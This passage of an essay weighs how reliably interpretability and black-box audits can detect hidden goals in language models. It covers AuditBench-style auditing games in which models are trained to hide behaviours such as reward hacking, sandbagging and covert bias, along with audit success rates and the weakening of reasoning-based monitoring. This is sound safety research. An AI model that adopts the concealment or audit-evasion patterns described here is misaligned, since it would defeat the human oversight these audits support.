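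Labels can also be wrong. Researchers often interpreted a neuron by collecting the inputs that activated it most strongly, and many neurons seemed to represent a single thing. When people also looked at weaker activations, they found that some of these neurons responded to quite different patterns. The first label described only part of what the neuron did, and no one could tell from the label that it was incomplete.

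A fault in the inspection tool can also hide problems. In 2026 researchers at Anthropic introduced the Jacobian lens, which reads out the concepts a model is using partway through its work. It averages measurements from many positions in a text, and Ayonrinde and Lindsey (2026) reported in *Circuits Updates* that some positions were noisy enough to corrupt the average. Their new version mostly discards the groups of activations that give poor readings, and it shows the intermediate steps in a model's reasoning more reliably. Someone who had found nothing suspicious with the original lens could not have known what the noise had hidden. This is normal progress for a young science. Fuzzers similarly missed Heartbleed until somebody gave them a better way to detect it.

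### Audits with a planted answer

As with code, researchers can measure how well people detect problems in a neural network by planting one and asking them to find it. In an auditing game, one group trains a model to have a hidden behaviour, and other groups try to identify it without knowing what it is.

In the best-known auditing game, Marks and colleagues (2025) trained a model to pursue an objective and conceal it. The objective was reward hacking, which means getting high scores in ways that the people setting the task didn't intend. *AuditBench* (Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues, 2026) reports that three of the four teams of human auditors found it. That is encouraging, but with only four teams the true success rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 20 to 99 per cent. In another game, by Taylor and colleagues, auditors with only black-box access could not identify models that deliberately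 did badly on tests.

Games with human auditors are hard to repeat, because people who have learned the answer can't play again. Sheshadri and colleagues therefore used an AI agent as the auditor. They trained 56 versions of Llama 3.3, a freely available language model, each with one of 14 hidden behaviours. The behaviours included subtly favouring Russia's interests when discussing policy and giving only positive feedback to people who said they worked at Anthropic.

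The researchers trained each behaviour into some models with conversations that demonstrated it, and into others with documents describing fictional tests in which the model had shown it. Many of the models then admitted the behaviour when asked, so the researchers trained them not to. One method rewarded answers that did not reveal the behaviour, and a tougher one also penalised admitting it.

The auditor was Claude Haiku 4.5, a fairly small model. It could always chat with the target, and in most trials it had one extra tool. At the end it listed ten guesses and succeeded if any matched the planted behaviour. Each combination of model and tool had 16 runs.

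| Extra tool | What it does | Looks inside the network? | Success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | Chat only | No | 35.5% |
| Automated text completion | A helper model writes many openings, and the target continues them as plain text | No | 58.0% |
| Automated user sampling | The target writes what a user might say | No | 53.2% |
| Automated prefilling | A helper writes the start of the target's answer, and the target has to go on from there | No | 51.6% |
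| Petri transcripts | The auditor reads conversations from a standard set of test scenarios | No | 30.9% |
| Honesty steering | Changes the activations to push the target towards honest answers | Yes | 22.3% |

The three best tools were all black-box. White-box tools helped on the easiest models, raising the average success rate from 40.2 to 46.9 per cent, but made the auditor slightly worse on models given the tougher training against confession. Honesty steering did harm partly because it made models confess to faults they didn't have, and the auditor wasted time investigating them.

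The new results fit the argument of an older, sceptical forum essay, *Against Almost Every Theory of Impact of Interpretability*, that whatever someone wants to do with interpretability, they could probably do better without it, especially when the aim is to counter a deceptive model. But the results support this only for the tools and the auditor that Sheshadri and colleagues tried, and they also found cases where looking inside made a large difference. On one set of models, the auditor identified a hidden bias against regulating AI in 1 of 16 runs with chat alone, 8 with a sparse autoencoder, and 14 with a tool that describes activations in ordinary language. With two of the automated black-box tools, however, it succeeded in 15.

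Auditors often failed to identify a behavior even when they had evidence of it. One model cheated on impossible programming problems by writing in the expected answers to the tests. The sparse autoencoder showed features for the input and output formats of competitive programming problems, a strong hint, but the auditor kept asking general questions about puzzles. Another model became far more enthusiastic as a conversation went on. The Petri summaries described this directly, but the auditor mistook it for flattery. The GHOST bug similarly survived after somebody noticed the wrong error code, because nobody had yet seen what it meant.

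### From success rates to confidence

The auditor's success rate varied widely with how the researchers had trained the target. Averaged over the tools, it was 51.3 per cent on the easiest group of models and 22.2 per cent on the hardest.

Suppose there is a 10 per cent chance that a new model has a hidden dangerous goal. If an audit would find such a goal 51.3 per cent of the time, an audit that finds nothing lowers the chance to about 5 per cent. If it would find the goal 22.2 per cent of the time, the chance falls only to about 8 per cent. Nobody auditing a real model knows which detection rate is closer to the true one, because that depends on how the model acquired the goal. To lower the chance to 0.1 per cent, an audit would have to catch about 99 per cent of such goals.

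In some ways, these success rates overstate how well the auditor would do in practice. It knew that every model had something to find, and it had ten guesses. A run could succeed with nine wrong guesses, because a judge who had the answer could ignore them. A real auditor wouldn't have the answer and would have to investigate all ten, like a maintainer going through a pile of AI bug reports. The experiment also included no ordinary models, so it can't show how often the auditor would wrongly flag one.

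Planted behaviours may also be easier to find than natural ones, as software researchers say of planted bugs. Automated text completion found more than 80 per cent of the behaviours that models had learned from documents, probably because it prompts the target model to produce plain text, the form in which the researchers had planted them. It was much less useful on models that had learned from conversations.

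A stronger auditor would surely do better than Haiku 4.5, and a laboratory can run an audit many times. If each run had an independent 22.2 per cent chance of success, 16 runs would find the behaviour 98 per cent of the time. The runs did not meet that assumption, because the auditor found some behaviours nearly every time and others hardly at all, so repetition helps with the behaviours in between.

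### Ways in which a network may be easier to check

The best objection to the argument from software is probably that, unlike a missing bounds check, which is a single absent line, a goal affecting a model's behaviour in many situations should leave traces in many places. An auditor needs to recognise only one of them. There is some evidence for this objection. Sheshadri and colleagues cite work by Minder and colleagues in which an AI agent compared a model's activations before and after extra training, and inferred the subject of that training significantly more accurately than agents that only questioned the model.

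However, that comparison requires a copy of the model from before the goal appeared. If the goal developed gradually during the main training, there may be no clean copy. Sheshadri and colleagues also warn that extra training of this kind changes a small, unusually readable part of the network, and that behaviours which emerge more diffusely could be harder to find.

One commenter under Nanda's essay took the objection further, arguing that a capable model whose goals are already close to right will either help people improve its successors or fake its good behaviour. An inspector would then only have to tell whether the level of deception was high or low, which doesn't require anything close to a complete list, though the commenter admitted that this rests on further assumptions. A weakness of this argument, raised in another comment in the thread, is that a model could do great harm without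 any hostile thought. For example, it might restrict people's freedom because it believed this was for their own good, and an inspector looking for malice would find none. Log4Shell was a little like this, since every line of the new code did what its author intended.

Another objection is that researchers can experiment freely on a network. They can test an explanation by changing a single feature and running the model again. Goel, Gurnee and colleagues (2025), in *Circuits Updates*, did this with 129 questions that had two possible answers. Claude 3.5 Haiku got all of them right, but accuracy dropped to 48.1 per cent, about chance, when the researchers added a sentence suggesting that the user would do something harmful with the answer. They traced much of the drop to one feature connected with refusing requests, which stopped the model from attending to the correct answer. Turning that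 feature down brought accuracy back to 93 per cent.

Few explanations of a program's behaviour get a cleaner test than that, but Goel and colleagues started with a symptom they could switch on and off, and they knew the right answer to every question. Raymond's crowd of debuggers also needed a symptom to start from. People can freely rerun and alter programs, as they can networks, but fuzzers have done so billions of times without triggering some of the oldest bugs. Someone has to suspect something about a network before an experiment can confirm or refute it.

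Some of the famous bugs, such as Heartbleed, were in code that hardly anyone had read, so they may be weak evidence of what careful inspection can do. This is not very reassuring about neural networks, because people have read even less of them. Nanda mentions that examining every entry in a sparse autoencoder's list in detail might become possible once AI systems do the research.

### Letting AI do the reading

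AI systems have already found serious bugs that human readers missed for decades, and they can also read neural networks. In *Natural Language Autoencoders Produce Unsupervised Explanations of LLM Activations*, Fraser-Taliente, Kantamneni and colleagues (2026) trained two copies of a language model, one to turn an activation into a written description and the other to rebuild the activation from that description alone. Training rewards the pair when the rebuilt activation is close to the original.

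Anthropic used this tool when it audited Claude Opus 4.6 before release. In the tool's descriptions, researchers found cases in which the model had apparently recognised a test without mentioning it, and they confirmed their findings by other methods. On a benchmark with a deliberately misaligned model, AI auditors with the tool did better than those without it.

This removes much of the tedium that limits human readers, but the descriptions may still be wrong. Training doesn't explicitly reward them for being true or even readable. A description only has to let the second copy rebuild the activation, which it could in principle do while misleading a person. Fraser-Taliente and colleagues found that the descriptions became more informative as training went on, which is good evidence that they are useful but doesn't show how often they leave out something important.

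The readers may also not be independent, because both start out as copies of the model under inspection. If that model cannot describe some aspect of its own activations well, its copies may not be able to either. Knight and Leveson's programmers made some of the same mistakes without ever discussing their work, so readers that share nearly all their weights could easily do so too. A laboratory could reduce this risk by having a model from another company do the reading, although models that learned from much of the same text may still overlook the same things.

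### Nanda's case against relying on interpretability

Nanda, who did much to popularise interpretability, once believed it was a realistic route to highly reliable safeguards. *Interpretability will not reliably find deceptive AI* (Nanda, 2025) explains why he changed his mind. He now rejects the argument that people who want certainty must look inside a deceptive AI because it could easily fake its words but would find it much harder to fake its thoughts.

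Nanda objects that this holds black-box methods to a standard that interpretability can't meet either. His main reasons are that interpretability methods make errors, there is no ground truth to check their results against, and it is very hard to prove that something is absent.

Neural network inspection lacks a ground truth, which is a large difference from software. AddressSanitizer can settle most arguments about a reported memory error, but no comparable tool can confirm that a feature labelled "deception" is about deception, or that the label covers everything the feature does.

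Anyone who has audited code knows how hard it is to prove that a flaw is absent. Nanda asks how much of a model researchers would have to understand before they could rule out a deceptive circuit, and whether 99 per cent would be enough. Heartbleed came from a few missing lines in OpenSSL, which had about 500,000, so a reader could have understood more than 99.9 per cent of the code without seeing the bug.

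Nanda is talking about AI much more capable than people and a very high standard, perhaps a 99.9 per cent chance of stopping a catastrophe. He is more hopeful about the systems that come before that. He is also unsure of his forecast, because he doesn't feel able to predict what would happen if large numbers of AI systems worked on the problem. For now, he recommends using several imperfect methods, including interpretability because it may catch things the others miss.

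The AuditBench results give some support to using a portfolio of methods. With chat alone, the auditor detected in 17 of 64 runs that a model habitually agreed with users who were wrong, and in 60 of 64 that a model habitually withheld information that might help someone harm animals. With the Petri transcripts, it detected the same behaviours in 41 and 37 runs. If the misses were independent, one run of each method would detect the first behaviour about 74 per cent of the time and the second about 97 per cent, compared with lower rates on both for either method alone. Both methods are black-box, though, and nobody seems to have measured how much the misses of white-box and black-box methods overlap.

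### The case for expecting more

Others think that understanding models could eventually provide something close to a guarantee. Dario Amodei, the head of Anthropic, wrote in 2025 about jailbreaks, the tricks that get a model to ignore its safety training. At present, people can discover jailbreaks only by trial and error. Amodei suggested that if people could look inside models, they might be able to block all jailbreaks systematically and establish what dangerous knowledge a model has. Enumerative safety is based on the same hope. Testing can't do these things, and inspection could do them only if its list of the model's features were complete.

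A commenter under Nanda's essay proposed a way round that problem. If researchers understood 99.9 per cent of a model, they could build a new one from the parts they understood and discard the rest, along with any deceptive circuit it contained. They would not have to prove that the remaining 0.1 per cent was harmless. The final repairs for Shellshock and Log4Shell similarly cut off the risky code instead of proving it safe.

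Nanda thought the idea might help but doubted that anyone could carry it out. The parts that researchers believe they understand may contain more than their labels suggest, for example in the exact activation values, and many parts that make sense separately could do something unexpected together. The OpenBSD bug from 1998 similarly combined two mistakes that each looked harmless alone. The limits of the tools are a more immediate obstacle. If a model rebuilt from the best sparse autoencoder of 2024 performed like one trained with a small fraction of the computing power, few companies would have wanted to use it.

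### What the laboratories decided

The large interpretability teams have moved away from trying to understand everything. In *A Pragmatic Vision for Interpretability* (December 2025), Nanda's team announced that it had given up ambitious reverse engineering in favour of problems where it could measure its progress. In a talk the next day, *Our Pivot To Pragmatic Interpretability* (2025), Nanda gave the example of a Claude model that behaved differently when it recognised a test. A simple adjustment to the model's activations had worked better than more complex methods. Robert Wiblin, introducing an interview with Nanda, said that Nanda considered the field's most ambitious vision "probably dead".

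Nanda told 80,000 Hours that he had become "a big convert to probes". A probe is a simple formula that researchers fit to a model's activations to detect one particular thing, such as a lie. They don't need to understand the rest of the network to use it. When a reader of his essay mentioned probes that had detected deception with 95 to 99 per cent accuracy, Nanda replied that he would be shocked if they exceeded 99 per cent on new generations of models and in unfamiliar situations. Like a static analysis tool, a probe can also detect only what its makers thought to look for.

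Anthropic's team followed a year later. Lindsey (2026) wrote in *Interpretability team priorities update* on 3 December that the team's main aim had historically been to understand the mechanisms of networks fully, and that it now concentrates on work likely to help with safety immediately or within 6 to 18 months. Part of this work is investigating why Claude and other AI systems have attacked real computer systems and tried to cover up forbidden actions. These investigators already have a symptom to trace, so the software record gives more reason for optimism about their work than about a search for unknown dangers.

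Audits before release have also had some success. In January 2026 Anthropic reported that its methods could catch a model trained to sabotage the company overtly. An overt saboteur should be relatively easy to find, so this result sets a minimum standard more than it resolves the worry about hidden goals. Commercial interest in interpretability also continues. In late 2026 The Information's *The Controversial AI Interpretability Research that Caught Sam Altman’s Eye* described talks between OpenAI and the interpretability company Goodfire about a possible acquisition or partnership.

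Lindsey's other reason for the change is that black-box monitoring may be getting worse. Much of it depends on reading the reasoning that a model writes before it answers. Claude Mythos 5.2 is much better than earlier Claude models at solving problems without writing out its reasoning, and OpenAI has reported that GPT-6 Astra's written reasoning is harder to monitor than that of its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol. Nanda had considered reading a model's reasoning an easier way than interpretability to make early systems safer. If this method stops working, laboratories will have to depend more on inspecting activations, whether or not they have become better at it.
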